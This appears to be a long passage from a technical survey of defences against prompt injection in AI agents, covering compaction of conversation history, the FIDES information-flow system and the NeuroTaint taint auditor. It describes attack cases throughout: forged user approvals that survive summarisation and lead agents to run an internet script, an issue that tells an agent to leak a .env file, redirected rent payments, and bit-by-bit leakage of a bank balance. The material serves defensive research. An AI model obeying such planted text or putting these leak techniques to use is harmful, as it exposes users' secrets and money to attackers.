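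A single agent can have the same problem when it summarises its own history. A model can read only a limited amount of text at once, and a coding agent that works for hours will reach the limit. *Context Compaction Theory* (2026) describes the usual solution, *compaction*. When the conversation nears the limit, the agent sends all of it to a model with a fixed request for a summary, then continues from the summary. *Inside the Scaffold* (2026) found that Aider, OpenHands, Gemini CLI, Codex and OpenCode all do this automatically.

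The ordinary program around the model, called the *harness*, stores each message with a field for its role, such as user, assistant or tool. Dabirsiaghi (2026), in *Compaction Laundering*, found that some harnesses throw this field away just before compaction. They *flatten* the conversation into one string, roughly like this:

```python
history = "\n".join(f"{m.role}: {m.text}" for m in messages)
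summary = model("Summarise this conversation.\n" + history)
```

Suppose the agent has read a web page that contains a line break, then the marker that opens a user's turn, then a sentence saying that some action has already been approved. In `history`, that sentence looks exactly like something the user typed. Part of the model's task is to record what the user said, so the attack works if the model records the approval as the user's, even if it doesn't obey the sentence.

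Other harnesses keep the roles *typed* by sending the summarising model a list of messages with the role fields intact. A forged marker inside a tool result is then just part of the tool result.

Dabirsiaghi planted the same forged approval in conversations for nine released harnesses. Each harness's own summary prompt was run with its own way of passing on the conversation, five times on each of three frontier models. A language model then judged whether the summary presented the approval as the user's. (A model from a different family agreed with the judge on all 18 summaries in a sample.)

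| Harness | Conversation sent as | Forged approval attributed to the user |
|---|---|---|
| pi, opencode, Aider | one string | 15 of 15 each |
| OpenHands | one string | 14 of 15 |
| Cline | one string | 13 of 15 |
| Codex, Gemini CLI, Qwen Code, Continue | typed messages | 0 of 15 each |

The forged text often made it into the typed harnesses' summaries too, but as something a document said.

The harnesses also differ in their summary prompts, so this comparison doesn't prove that flattening is the cause. Two other tests are stronger evidence. With pi's prompt, summaries attributed the forged approval to the user 87% of the time when the marker was in front of it and 6% when it wasn't. When Dabirsiaghi ran Gemini CLI's prompt on flattened text, which the real product never does, the rate was 69%.

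Gemini CLI's prompt includes a warning against injected instructions. On flattened text, the warning lowered the rate from 83% to 62% with an OpenAI model, but only from 53% to 46% with an Anthropic model.

With pi, the summary presented the forgery as the user's words at every conversation length tested. This held in all three runs at each of seven lengths, from about 2,800 tokens (words or pieces of words) to 908,000, close to the model's limit. Repeated summarising didn't remove the forgery either. Dabirsiaghi compacted 54 conversations five times in a row, and the verdict stayed the same throughout in 52.

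### From a false memory to an action

A false summary does harm only if the agent acts on it. In one test, the summary recorded an instruction to leave a certain directory alone, and the next task required changing a file there. Agents planned to avoid the file in 98% of cases when the user had given the instruction, 92% when it came from a tool result, and 6% when nobody had given it. An attacker could use this to keep a code-review agent away from a file with a backdoor.

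Dabirsiaghi also tested whether a forged approval would lead an agent to run a script from the internet, using a harmless script in an isolated container. With pi's summaries, the agent ran it in five of five attempts after a conversation of about 26,000 tokens, but in only two of five after 263,000. A genuine approval from the user gave the same results. So the agent seems to have been more careful about running scripts in general after the longer conversation, not better at spotting the forgery.

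These staged tests used synthetic conversations. The summary went to a fresh agent that had never seen the web page, had only one tool, and had nobody to ask for permission. In real use, the agent that reads the page also continues after compaction, and it may have objected to the script in the meantime.

A live test with the actual pi program included this step. A scripted user repeated the same session in six pairs, and the two sessions in each pair differed only in whether a web page contained the forged line. In three of the six attacked sessions, the agent first refused to run the script, then ran it after compacting its history. This did not happen in any of the five usable clean sessions. In the sixth clean session, the agent ran the script before compaction.

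Three executions in six attacked sessions, against none in five clean ones, is weak evidence. If the forged line made no difference, all three would still fall among the attacked sessions about one time in eight. The result also depended on what the user typed next. These figures come from sessions where the user asked a neutral question about what to do next. A bare "ok" never led to an execution, and a mildly urgent message led to executions in clean sessions too. The live test shows that the whole chain can happen in a real product, but it doesn't measure how often.

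The main obstacle to the attack was the agent's own objections. In one attacked session, the summary included all the agent's concerns about the script, followed by a statement that the user had approved running it. In a later staged test, where the conversation included a thorough written review ending in a refusal, the agent ran the script in only one of 40 attacked runs.

Whether this script works also depends on the harness. Pi runs commands without user approval by default, whereas Codex's default settings cut off network access and would block the script regardless of the agent's reasoning.

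### Escaping and checking against the user's words

The flattening bug closely resembles *log forging*, an old attack on web servers. A visitor submits text containing a line break followed by what looks like a log entry, and an administrator reading the log can't tell that the entry is fake. SQL injection is similar but uses a quotation mark instead of a line break. Dabirsiaghi reported the bug to the five affected projects under CWE-74, the standard catalogue number for this kind of injection flaw, and CWE-1427, its counterpart for model prompts.

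Database programmers have two standard fixes for this problem. They can *escape* special characters, so that the database reads a quotation mark in someone's name as part of the name, or they can send the command and the values separately. Multi-CaMeL takes the second approach. Dabirsiaghi recommends the first for the harnesses that flatten messages, which means making a small change to one function so that it alters any role marker inside a tool result before joining the messages.

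Escaping works less well for a model than for a database, though. A database follows a fixed grammar, so a correctly escaped value can never become a command, but a model can still misattribute a sentence with no marker in front of it. This happened 6% of the time with pi's prompt and 28% of the time with Gemini CLI's prompt after Dabirsiaghi removed its warning. Dabirsiaghi's estimate of what escaping would achieve comes from these runs rather than from tests of a repaired harness. Typed roles also rely on the model to respect them. The model respected them in all 60 runs, but the true failure rate could still be almost 5%.

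A harness can also check the summary afterwards, because it still has the user's real messages in memory. Dabirsiaghi's check compares the wording of each claim the summary attributes to the user with those messages and with the untrusted text. If the claim is closer to the untrusted text, the check marks it as unattributed. This caught 77% of the forgeries and wrongly marked 2% of legitimate claims. A stricter setting caught 82% but wrongly marked 9%. Requiring an exact match with the user's own text was useless because good summaries paraphrase, so it wrongly marked at least 72% of legitimate claims.

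This check is meant to recover a lost label from the wording of the text, so an attacker who imitates the user's writing would probably get past it. Dabirsiaghi didn't test it against anyone trying to evade it.

### A summary in the user's place

Typed roles protect the messages that go into a summary, but the summary is a new string, and the harness has to give it a role too. Fei, Fei and colleagues (2026), in *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction*, recorded 1,108 automatic compactions in Claude Code and Codex. Every time, the harness inserted the summary as a message from the user. Codex is one of the four harnesses that scored 0% in Dabirsiaghi's test. (Agents that store parts of a conversation as long-term memories can lose the same distinction, which *When Memory Becomes Authority* (2026) calls "authority collapse".)

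This is a serious problem for defences that use the user's message to decide what the agent may do. *Progent*, for example, has a model turn the user's request into a list of permitted tool calls, and blocks everything else. Fei and colleagues had Progent write a new list for each request. In one of their tests, the user gives the landlord's account number and asks what a notice says. The notice is the attacker's, and it mentions a different account for the rent as a fact, without giving any instruction. The conversation is then compacted, and the user asks the agent to pay this month's rent.

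When Progent worked from the summary, its list allowed a payment to the attacker's account in 290 of 320 sessions (91%). With a stronger model writing the list, the share was 59%. The list never allowed the payment when Progent worked from the user's own messages.

The models that wrote the summaries were good at spotting injected instructions. They flagged the attacker's account in 219 of the 220 summaries that kept it. But they rarely flagged an account number presented as ordinary data, and Fei and colleagues prove that no check on the text alone can do this reliably. Let $p_L$ be the probability that a check allows a payment to the account in a legitimate notice, and $p_A$ the probability that it allows one to the account in a forged notice. Then

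$$p_L - p_A \le \mathrm{TV}(P_L, P_A),$$

where $P_L$ and $P_A$ are the probability distributions of everything the check reads in the two cases. The *total variation distance*, TV, is 0 if the distributions are identical and 1 if they never overlap. If the attacker copies the format of real notices and picks a plausible account number, the distance is close to 0. A check that allows 95% of genuine notices must then allow about 95% of forged ones too. A better prompt or a smarter model won't help, because the missing information isn't in the text.

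Under the join rule, a summary is labelled untrusted if any part of the conversation it summarises is untrusted. This is safe, but the agent is then allowed to do very little, because the user's own request has become part of an untrusted text.

Fei and colleagues avoid this by keeping the user's messages out of the merge. Trusted code attaches a cryptographic tag to each user message when it arrives and, at compaction, copies all the tagged messages unchanged and in order. The agent still reads the summary, but Progent reads only the tagged messages, and it permits nothing if one is missing, altered or out of place. The tags matter when the agent can edit the files where the harness stores its history. Otherwise, a separate list of user messages is enough. OpenAI has built something similar into the Codex component that reviews risky actions, and since October 2026 that component has attributed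 summaries to the assistant.

In 40 attacked AgentDojo episodes with the summary inserted as a user message, the attacker succeeded 7 times and the agent completed 9 tasks. With the full repair, which includes inserting the summary as a tool result instead, the attacker never succeeded and the agent completed 19 tasks, compared with 27 without compaction. Moving the summary without the rest of the repair did almost as well in this test, with no successful attacks and 18 completed tasks. But Progent then receives only the latest message. In the rent example, that message was a payment request with no account number, and Progent's list allowed a payment to anyone.

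The repair can't help if the user gives no account number and asks the agent to pay whatever the notice specifies. The user's messages then contain no account number to compare with the one in the notice, so the agent will treat a forged notice like a real one unless it can verify who sent it.

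## FIDES: tracking data while letting secrets steer decisions

CaMeL's planner has to finish its program before it sees any data, so it often fails when the right next step depends on an earlier result. *FIDES* (Flow Integrity Deterministic Enforcement System), which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft in 2025, keeps the ordinary agent loop. Its planner can choose each call after seeing earlier results, though labels determine how much of each result it sees.

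### The context label and hidden variables

In FIDES, every message, tool call, argument and tool result has a label. Tool results are usually structured data, so each field can have its own label. For example, an e-mail's arrival time may be trusted while its text is not.

When the agent calls a tool $f$, the result gets the label

$$\ell_{\text{result}}=\ell_{\text{call}}\;\sqcup\;\bigsqcup_i \ell_{\text{arg}_i}\;\sqcup\;\bigsqcup_{x\in R(f)}\ell_x$$

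where $\ell_{\text{call}}$ is the label of the decision to make the call and $R(f)$ is the stored data that the tool may read. Anything the tool may write gets the same label. Searching the web for a secret project name therefore gives a secret result, even though anyone can read the pages it finds.

FIDES gives each of the planner's replies the context label. To limit the resulting label creep, it checks each field of a result before adding it to the conversation. If a field would raise the context label, FIDES stores it in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name, while the other fields stay visible.

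The planner can pass a variable to another tool by name, and the contents keep their own label. It can also use the `query_llm` tool to ask a quarantined model about the contents. The answer goes into a new variable, labelled with the join of the context label and the labels of everything the quarantined model read. If the planner needs to read a variable itself, it calls `inspect`, which raises the context label for the rest of the conversation.

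### Two checks before a tool call

FIDES checks labels just before it makes a tool call. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) calls FIDES's two basic policies *trusted action* and *permitted flow*.

The trusted action policy allows a consequential call, such as a payment, only if the planner decided on it in a trusted context. The policy can also require particular arguments to be trusted. For a payment, it should require this of the account number, but perhaps not of the reference text.

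The permitted flow policy allows a tool to send data only if every recipient may read it. An injection can still trigger the call, but the policy limits what the attacker can gain from it.

In Kolluri and colleagues' version, a tool that sends data must satisfy only one of the two policies. If the planner decided in a trusted context to send the data, FIDES assumes the user wanted this. Otherwise, the data may go only to people already allowed to read it. This is a form of *robust declassification*, which means that an attacker can't cause a release that the confidentiality labels forbid.

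Suppose a user asks the agent to summarise the three latest e-mails and send the summary to Priya on Slack. The e-mails are untrusted and secret, (U, H) in the notation of the first section, and the user's request is trusted and public, (T, L).

| Step | Label of the new data | Context label in FIDES | Context label without hiding |
|---|---|---|---|
| The user makes the request | (T, L) | (T, L) | (T, L) |
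| `read_emails(number=3)` | (U, H) | (T, L); the model sees only `#emails` | (U, H) |
| `query_llm("Summarise", #emails)` | (U, H) | (T, L); the model sees only `#summary` | not needed, since the planner can write the summary |
| `send_message("Priya", #summary)` | call and recipient (T, L), message (U, H) | allowed | refused, unless Priya may read all three e-mails |

As in any dual-LLM design, an injection in one of the e-mails can still spoil the summary, for example by making the quarantined model return an empty one.

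In the invoice example, the planner could make the payment with `pay(#account, amount)`. The decision to pay is trusted but the account number isn't, so the outcome depends on whether the policy checks that argument. Costa and colleagues say the policies in their tests don't check tool arguments, and under a policy like that the attacker would get the money.

### The guarantee for integrity

In a later version of the paper, Costa and colleagues claim noninterference for integrity, meaning that untrusted data can't influence the decision to take a consequential action.

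To see why this is plausible, imagine two mailboxes that differ only in the text of the e-mails. As long as the planner leaves that text in variables, its model receives the same conversation for both mailboxes and, if the model is deterministic, requests the same calls. If the planner inspects a variable, the conversations may differ, but by then both contexts are untrusted and FIDES blocks every consequential call.

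This also catches the if-statement in the invoice example. The planner can't choose between the supplier's two accounts without learning whether the e-mail contains "we have changed banks". Once it inspects the answer, the context becomes untrusted, whether the answer is yes or no. FIDES avoids CaMeL's missed-assignment fault here because it raises the context's label when the planner reads the condition and never lowers it during the conversation.

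But the context label disappears when the conversation ends, so a notes file that the agent updates only under some condition can still mislead the agent in a later conversation. Denning found a similar flaw in ADEPT-50.

### What explicit secrecy covers

For confidentiality, FIDES guarantees only explicit secrecy. Schoepe and colleagues defined this property in 2016, and it is close to the *weak secrecy* Volpano defined in 1999.

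The idea is to run the program once and write down the operations it performed, leaving out the conditions that led to them. This gives a function $g$ from starting data to final data. The program satisfies explicit secrecy if, for every run from a starting state $d_1$ and every state $d_2$,

$$d_1 =_L d_2 \;\Rightarrow\; g(d_1) =_L g(d_2).$$

In other words, repeating the *same operations* with different secrets must give the same public results. Under noninterference, the whole program would instead run again on $d_2$ and could take a different path.

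This program satisfies explicit secrecy and still leaks:

```python
rich = False                 # public
if balance > 10000:          # secret
    rich = True
```

With a balance of 25,000, the program sets `rich` to false, then to true. Repeating those operations with any other balance also gives true. With a balance of 4,000, the program only sets `rich` to false, which gives false whatever the balance. Each path passes the test by itself, but anyone who reads `rich` learns which path the program took. The line `rich = balance` would fail the test because its result changes with the secret.

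A FIDES agent can leak in a similar way. Suppose it has stored 16 links from a web search in separate variables, inspected a page that contains an injection, and then read the user's bank balance. The injection is an instruction to open one of the links, chosen according to four bits of the balance. If the model typed the address itself, the address would have the context's secret label and fail the permitted-flow check. But the agent can pass the stored link, which is public, and permitted flow doesn't check the label of the decision to open it. If the attacker runs the 16 pages, they can see in the server log which one the agent opened and learn those four bits. Five such calls reveal a 20-bit balance.

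Agents can also leak information through their choices without a prompt injection. In *Confuse the Model, Control the Flow*, Shim, Karim and colleagues (2026) gave agents a shared page that mixed real and invented facts about a person and asked them to clean it up. The entries that an agent refused to delete were the real ones. On a live agent with access to Gmail and Notion, this attack had a leak rate of 34.7% against a defence that asks a model to spot privacy violations. The researchers didn't test the attack on FIDES.

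### Is the compromise reasonable?

Costa and colleagues chose explicit secrecy because full noninterference would forbid almost any public action after the agent has read a secret. Personal assistants read private calendars and mailboxes all day, so noninterference would rule out much of their work. Other practical systems have made the same choice, including TaintDroid, which tracks private data in Android apps.

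The compromise also stops the fastest leaks. An attacker who can copy text into an outgoing message can get a whole mailbox at once, whereas the link trick leaks four bits per call. That rate makes it hard to steal a long document, but not a PIN or the answer to "does this person have cancer?"

Garby and colleagues object that explicit secrecy is weakest where data and control are interchangeable, as they often are in an agent. The definition in the original FIDES paper, for example, treats the conversation as part of the program, and only the tools' stored data as data. Suppose an agent looks up a balance of 25,000 and then types "25000" into a public message. The recorded operation is "send 25000", which does the same thing whatever the balance is. Read literally, the definition therefore allows an agent to copy a secret outright, as long as the copy goes through the conversation. FIDES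 itself is stricter, because it gives the typed number the context's secret label, so the message fails the permitted-flow check.

### Letting small values through

Hiding untrusted text makes some ordinary requests impossible to carry out. For example, a user might ask the agent to check three e-mails for a meeting request and create a calendar event if there is one. The planner has to find out whether there is a meeting request, but reading the answer makes its context untrusted, so it is no longer allowed to create the event.

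FIDES has an optional exception for this. The planner can require `query_llm` to answer in a fixed format, such as a boolean or a choice from a list, and the inference software enforces the format as the model generates its answer. FIDES then adds the type to the label. Types are ordered by how much information they can carry, so a boolean ranks below a three-item list, which ranks below free text. A policy may accept an untrusted boolean but refuse an untrusted string, because a single yes or no has little room for an injection. In the calendar example, the planner inspects the boolean, then has the quarantined model put the event's details into a variable that the planner never reads.

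One boolean carries at most one bit, but a planner may ask many questions. If it inspects $k$ values and the $i$-th has $m_i$ possible answers, together they can carry up to

$$\log_2(m_1 m_2\cdots m_k)=\sum_{i=1}^{k}\log_2 m_i \text{ bits.}$$

$k$ booleans carry $k$ bits, so 20 booleans are enough to encode the bank balance, matching the number of runs in the attack on CaMeL's retry loop. A choice from three items carries about 1.58 bits, so 13 such choices are also enough.

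FIDES's labels don't record how many boolean answers have entered the context. Joining the type "boolean" with itself gives "boolean", so the context has the same label after 20 answers as after one, and a policy that checks only labels will treat both cases the same way. To limit the total, FIDES would need a separate counter.

Even one bit may be too many for integrity, since a single accepted boolean again lets the e-mail determine which of the supplier's two accounts is used. The exception is safer if every possible answer has a harmless result, such as an unwanted calendar entry.

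Garby and colleagues also object that releases are hard to audit. When a policy lets a value through, nothing in that run distinguishes a release the designers intended from a leak. "Is there a meeting request?" and "Is the seventh bit of the PIN a 1?" both produce a boolean, and the two answers can have identical labels. An auditor could read the questions in the log, but would have to judge each one by its meaning, and labels were meant to avoid relying on such judgements. Garby and colleagues prefer to make every release an explicit instruction in the program, which an auditor can at least find.

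### AgentDojo results

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo with the exception for small values switched off, because most of the tasks don't need it. The table shows the percentage of tasks that agents using OpenAI's o1 model completed when they were not under attack.

| Agent | Workspace | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent, no policy checks | 70.0 | 82.0 | 96.2 | 87.6 |
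| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 48.0 | 75.0 | 37.5 | 17.1 |
| FIDES, no policy checks | 77.5 | 75.0 | 78.8 | 79.0 |
| FIDES with checks | 64.5 | 68.0 | 56.2 | 54.3 |

With checks on, FIDES completed on average 16 percentage points more of the tasks than the ordinary agent, but 23 points fewer than the ordinary agent without checks. The gains are largest in Slack, where the first untrusted message would otherwise block most later actions. In travel, FIDES does worse than the ordinary agent even with checks on, because many of the tools are allowed to run in an untrusted context anyway, so the variables only hinder the agent.

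FIDES's performance also depends on how well the model handles variables. With the older GPT-4o, FIDES's average advantage was only 8 points, and the model sometimes confused variable names or made needless calls that raised the context label. Some tasks are impossible under FIDES with any model. For example, if the user asks the agent to follow the instructions in a file, reading the file makes the context untrusted and the agent can no longer make payments.

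In the security test with GPT-4o, 152 attacks succeeded against the ordinary agent without checks, 21 against FIDES without checks, and none against either agent with checks. AgentDojo's scoring counted three successes against FIDES with checks, but Costa and colleagues discounted them because the benchmark counts some tool calls as successful attacks even if the policy blocked them, as well as some messages that the policy deliberately allows.

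The perfect score is less impressive because the FIDES evaluation marked a field as untrusted if at least one of AgentDojo's attacks uses it. This tests the mechanism cleanly, but it means that none of those attacks could come from data wrongly marked as trusted.

In real use, somebody has to decide which fields an attacker can influence, and it is easy to get this wrong. One banking task asks the agent to change the user's password if there has been a suspicious transaction. FIDES hid the transaction's description but showed its amount, which counted as trusted. The model judged the amount suspicious and changed the password, in line with the policy. But whoever sends a payment chooses its amount, so an outsider might be able to trigger the same action. (TaintBench, which the next section covers, tests for lost flows directly and includes FIDES as a baseline.)

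### Planning for fewer approvals

Kolluri and colleagues, several of whom also built FIDES, argue that these comparisons are unfair to label-based defences. An agent without labels usually has to ask a person before every consequential action, because it can't tell which ones are safe. Benchmarks don't count those requests against the undefended agent, but they count a task as failed if the defended agent would have needed to ask even once.

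They propose two measures, the *human-in-the-loop load* and TCR@$k$. The load is the total number of approvals an agent needs on the tasks it completes. TCR@$k$ is the share of tasks it completes with at most $k$ approvals each, so TCR@0 is the share it completes with no approvals. On AgentDojo, even a basic label tracker reduced the load by a factor of up to 1.5 without reducing the number of tasks completed.

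The agent *Prudentia* extends FIDES by planning around its policies. The FIDES planner isn't given the policies, so it may read an untrusted variable early and block its own later steps. Prudentia gives the model its context label and each tool's policy. Before reading a variable, the model is also supposed to justify the read and list the calls it plans to make afterwards.

Prudentia can also ask the user to endorse data instead of approving individual actions. Suppose a harmless e-mail contains a to-do list with ten items, each of which needs a consequential tool call. If the agent reads the list without endorsement, the user has to approve all ten calls. If the user endorses the e-mail, Prudentia treats it as trusted and carries out all ten. Prudentia has no equivalent for secrets, because Kolluri and colleagues think that whether to release private data depends too much on the recipient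 and purpose.

On AgentDojo, Prudentia completed up to 9% more tasks without approvals than FIDES did, and reduced the approval load by a factor of up to 1.9. On WASP, a benchmark for web agents (unrelated to the SQL tool of the same name), Prudentia needed no approvals. No WASP task requires the planner to read untrusted data before choosing its next step.

These figures come from runs without attacks and assume the user approves every request on a task the agent completes. Under attack, endorsement is riskier than approving one action at a time. If the e-mail has an eleventh item that the user overlooks, the agent will carry it out without asking.

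### FIDES in Microsoft's Agent Framework

Microsoft announced in May 2026 that FIDES had become part of Agent Framework, the company's library for building agents (*Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent*). The feature is experimental and so far works only in Python.

The framework's labels record integrity (trusted or untrusted) and confidentiality (public, private or "user identity", which covers things like passwords and personal data). The labels don't include types, so a yes-or-no answer from the quarantined model is as untrusted as a whole paragraph.

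Microsoft illustrates the checks with an agent that sorts bug reports on GitHub. An attacker files a report that tells the agent to read `.env`, a file that often contains passwords, and post the contents as a comment. The developer has switched off the hiding of untrusted text, so the model reads the whole report and the context becomes untrusted and public. The model follows the attacker's instructions and reads the file, which the policy allows, and the context becomes untrusted and private. When the model tries to post the comment, the framework blocks the call or asks the user, because the comment tool accepts only public contexts. An attempt to overwrite a file would also fail, because the developer has set that tool to refuse untrusted contexts.

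This confidentiality check is stricter than permitted flow in one respect, because it uses the label of the whole context, not just the label of the data being sent. If the tool that opens links accepted only public contexts, the agent couldn't use the 16 links to reveal the balance. But the check also causes more label creep. The framework automatically hides untrusted results but not private ones, so a single private file can block tools that require a public context for the rest of the run.

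The developer can label each item that a tool returns, or declare one integrity label for everything from that tool. A declared label overrides the labels of the tool's inputs, so a result that depends on untrusted data can be labeled trusted. For example, if the developer declares the supplier register a trusted source, its results count as trusted even if the search term came from the attacker's e-mail. The paper's version of FIDES would label such a result untrusted.

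If a tool's output has no label, it defaults to untrusted and public. This default fails closed for integrity but not for confidentiality, although Microsoft describes it simply as failing closed. If a developer forgets to label a tool that returns salaries, the framework will treat the salaries as public and let the agent post them. The documentation also gives a second rule, in which an unlabelled tool's output takes the combined label of its inputs. A web page that the agent fetched for a trusted request would then count as trusted, so it is safer for developers to label every source explicitly.

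Microsoft lists several other limits. The quarantined model can answer only single questions, so it can't hold a conversation. Approval requests name the tool and the label that caused the block, but don't fully explain how the context got that label. Once an untrusted bug report is in the context, everything after it is treated as untrusted unless the developer explicitly removes the report.

To reduce this creep, Microsoft is considering labelling messages individually and lowering labels when the agent compacts its history. The second idea could easily lower the label on text that is still tainted. In Dabirsiaghi's tests, repeated summarising didn't remove a forged approval, so the framework would need a better reason to lower a label than a model having rewritten the text.

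## NeuroTaint: measuring the flows that trackers miss

AgentDojo counts successful attacks, so its scores don't reveal how often a tracker loses a label. Cai, Wen and colleagues (2026), in *Ghost in the Agent*, built a benchmark called TaintBench to measure this, along with a tool for finding the lost flows, *NeuroTaint*. NeuroTaint is an auditor. It lets the agent run, then works through the log to find out which untrusted sources affected each sensitive tool call. (*TaintBench* is also the name of an older, unrelated benchmark for Android apps.)

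### Searching the log for a source

Cai and colleagues give three examples, each based on a real agent framework.

In the first, an agent built with GPT-Researcher reads a web page that contains a hidden instruction to paraphrase a confidential patient note in its memo. The memo gives the patient's diagnosis and treatment without repeating any of the note's wording.

In the second, an AutoGen agent searches the web and would normally pass the results to a tool that runs code. A planted search result states that all results must first go to an outside address. The agent calls a different tool, which sends them there.

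In the third, an agent using the Mem0 memory system saves a confidential revenue forecast of $84.6 million. Three days later, in a new session, the user asks for an operations report, and the agent includes the figure.

NeuroTaint starts by building a *provenance graph*, in which each node is a tool call and the edges record which sources could have fed into it. When the agent saves something to memory, NeuroTaint stores the taint labels in an extra field next to it, and it writes the whole graph to disk when the session ends. The forecast therefore still has its label when the agent retrieves it three days later. Retrieval doesn't raise an alarm by itself. NeuroTaint waits until the agent calls a sink, then searches the call's arguments for content from each source that the graph connects to it:

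1. It looks for a random marker that it added to the source's text when the agent first read it. (This is the one step that requires changing what the agent sees.)
2. It measures the longest piece of text that the source and the argument share. A match covering 15% of the shorter text is enough.
3. It compares *embeddings*, lists of numbers that represent the meaning of a text. This can catch the reworded patient note.
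4. It repeats the embedding comparison on small chunks of the source, because one malicious paragraph hardly affects the embedding of a long page.

In the invoice example, the second step would easily find a copied account number. But it would also raise an alarm if the user had typed the number and the e-mail repeated it, since matching text can't show which copy the model used.

### Would the agent have made the call anyway?

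If the search finds nothing, NeuroTaint runs a *counterfactual test*. It replaces the source's text in the log with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found". It then shows a language model both versions and asks whether the agent would have made the same call with the placeholder. If the answer is no, NeuroTaint reports an implicit flow.

This can catch the if-statement from the invoice example. If the e-mail contains "we have changed banks" and the agent pays the supplier's second account, removing the e-mail also removes the reason for choosing that account.

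The test resembles the two-run comparison in the definition of noninterference, but the second model predicts what the agent would have done instead of NeuroTaint running the agent again. The model also estimates its own confidence score.

NeuroTaint also tests only one replacement, whereas noninterference covers every possible input. Suppose the user has specified the amount, and an attacker who controls the supplier's old account deletes the sentence about changing banks from the e-mail. The agent pays the old account. The placeholder doesn't mention a change of banks either, so the agent would probably have paid the same account if it had seen the placeholder instead, and the test finds no flow. CaMeL also allows this payment because of its missed-assignment fault.

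Repeating a message can also defeat the test, because NeuroTaint replaces one source at a time. If two e-mails announce the change of banks and NeuroTaint replaces either one, the agent would still pay the second account because of the other.

Cai and colleagues illustrate this test with the AutoGen example, and write that such attacks leave "no data footprint" in the tool call. But in the printed example, the attacker's web address appears in both the search result and the call, so the text search should already have found it. The choice between two registered accounts is a clearer example.

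### Results on TaintBench

TaintBench contains 400 scenarios, 20 on each of 20 agent frameworks. In half of them, untrusted content is supposed to reach or influence a sink. Cai and colleagues ran each scenario five times with GPT-4.1 mini as the agent's model and counted a detector as raising an alarm if it did so in most of the runs. They compared NeuroTaint with a baseline they call FIDES.

*Precision* is the share of alarms that are correct, *recall* is the share of real flows that a detector finds, and *F1* combines the two into one score. NeuroTaint had a precision of 0.921, a recall of 0.935 and an F1 of 0.928. The baseline's scores were 0.505, 0.540 and 0.522. This is how many alarms each raised:

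| Type of scenario | Real flow? | Scenarios | NeuroTaint | FIDES baseline |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Exact marker copied | yes | 15 | 15 | 9 |
| Text copied or nearly copied | yes | 45 | 45 | 36 |
| Flow spread over fragments of a document | yes | 15 | 15 | 6 |
| Text paraphrased over several steps | yes | 42 | 35 | 31 |
| Borderline similarity in meaning | yes | 3 | 2 | 3 |
| Implicit control flow | yes | 40 | 37 | 17 |
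| Flow across sessions or agents | yes | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Source marked trusted or not labelled | yes | 10 | 10 | 1 |
| Source and sink both used, but no flow | no | 140 | 1 | 94 |
| Output on the same topic as the source | no | 14 | 14 | 9 |
| Output the model could write from memory | no | 6 | 1 | 3 |
| Other clean runs | no | 40 | 0 | 0 |

NeuroTaint raised a false alarm in all 14 scenarios where the output was on the same topic as the source but didn't come from it. These scenarios are a small part of the benchmark, but a research agent mostly reads and writes about one topic, so such false alarms could be much more common in practice.

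### What the baseline's misses show

The baseline called FIDES missed 23 of the 40 implicit flows and even 6 of the 15 exact copies. These misses are odd because Costa and colleagues' FIDES assigns the context's label to every call the model writes. A tracker that does this shouldn't miss a flow within one session if the source is labeled correctly. In the AutoGen example, it would label the call untrusted because the search result was already in the context.

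Cai and colleagues say the baseline uses labels and "known tool paths", and treats a path from a source to a sink as strong evidence of a flow. They gave it the same list of sources and sinks as NeuroTaint, but it raised no alarms on four frameworks (Google ADK, AgentScope, browser-use and Skyvern), which account for 40 of its 92 misses. Perhaps its list of paths didn't match the tools in those frameworks.

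That can't be the whole explanation, though. Of the 92 misses, 58 involved neither separate sessions or agents nor a source that was unlabelled or marked as trusted. Even if all 40 misses on the four silent frameworks were among these, 18 would remain. The baseline therefore doesn't behave like a tracker that labels the whole context, and its score of 17 out of 40 says little about the real FIDES. (The real system would also have hidden much of the untrusted text from the planner, so the agent might never have made some of these calls.)

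A detector that raised an alarm in every scenario would have an F1 of 0.667, which is better than the baseline's. A tracker that labelled the whole context would probably score about the same. If it found all 160 flows that stay within a session and come from correctly labelled sources, missed the other 40, and raised a false alarm in every flow-free scenario except the clean runs, its F1 would be 0.62. If its labels also survived in memory and in messages between agents, it would find 190 flows and score 0.69. It would then find slightly more flows than NeuroTaint did, but raise 160 false alarms instead of 16.

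By this rough estimate, NeuroTaint's main advantage over a proper context label is that it raises fewer false alarms, and even that may be overstated. NeuroTaint normally requires an embedding similarity of at least 0.60, but Cai and colleagues write that "safe-control policies" use a threshold of 0.95. If these policies apply to scenarios without a flow, as the name suggests, NeuroTaint required stronger evidence in the scenarios where an alarm would be wrong. An auditor working on a real log couldn't do the same, because they wouldn't know which cases those were.

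TaintBench may favour NeuroTaint in other ways, since the same people built both. Its types of flow closely match NeuroTaint's detection steps, including a category for NeuroTaint's random markers. Two of the researchers did check every scenario template independently, and they finalised the labels before comparing the detectors. But on two benchmarks built by others, NeuroTaint and the baseline were almost tied, with F1 scores of 0.994 and 0.993 on the basic version of InjecAgent and 0.760 each on part of ToolEmu. Those benchmarks test whether an action was unsafe, not where its contents came from, so they provide weaker evidence about flow tracking.

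TaintBench's labels also describe what is supposed to happen in a scenario, not what happened in a particular run. If the agent refuses to make the call, no flow occurs, but the scenario still counts as a miss. NeuroTaint's recall fell to 0.547 when the agent ran on Claude Opus 4.6, probably in large part because the model refused more often.

### Labels on stored memories

Relative to the number of scenarios, the baseline did worse on flows across sessions than on any other kind except flows with badly labelled sources. Ouyang and Hou (2026) point out in *MemLineage* that FIDES's labels last for only one run of the planner, so a later session has them only if someone saves them with the data.

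NeuroTaint saves the memories' taint labels, but Ouyang and Hou object that an attacker who can write to the memory store can change them. Their system, MemLineage, signs each memory together with its label. It also records which earlier memories a new one came from, and weights each link between 0 and 1 by how strongly the earlier memory influenced the new one. An untrusted label passes along every link whose weight is above a threshold, and MemLineage refuses sensitive actions based on a memory with an untrusted label.

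The threshold reduces label creep but can also lose labels. In one of Ouyang and Hou's tests, the first link has a weight of 0.9, and each further summary reduces the weight by 30%. The weight of link $K$ is then

$$w_K = 0.9\times 0.7^{K-1}.$$

With a threshold of 0.3, the label survives four summaries, since $w_4\approx 0.31$. The fifth link has a weight of about 0.22, so the fifth summary counts as trusted. An attacker could exploit this by planting text that the agent will summarise repeatedly. The weights in this test came from a fixed schedule, so it isn't clear how quickly a real model's estimates would fall.

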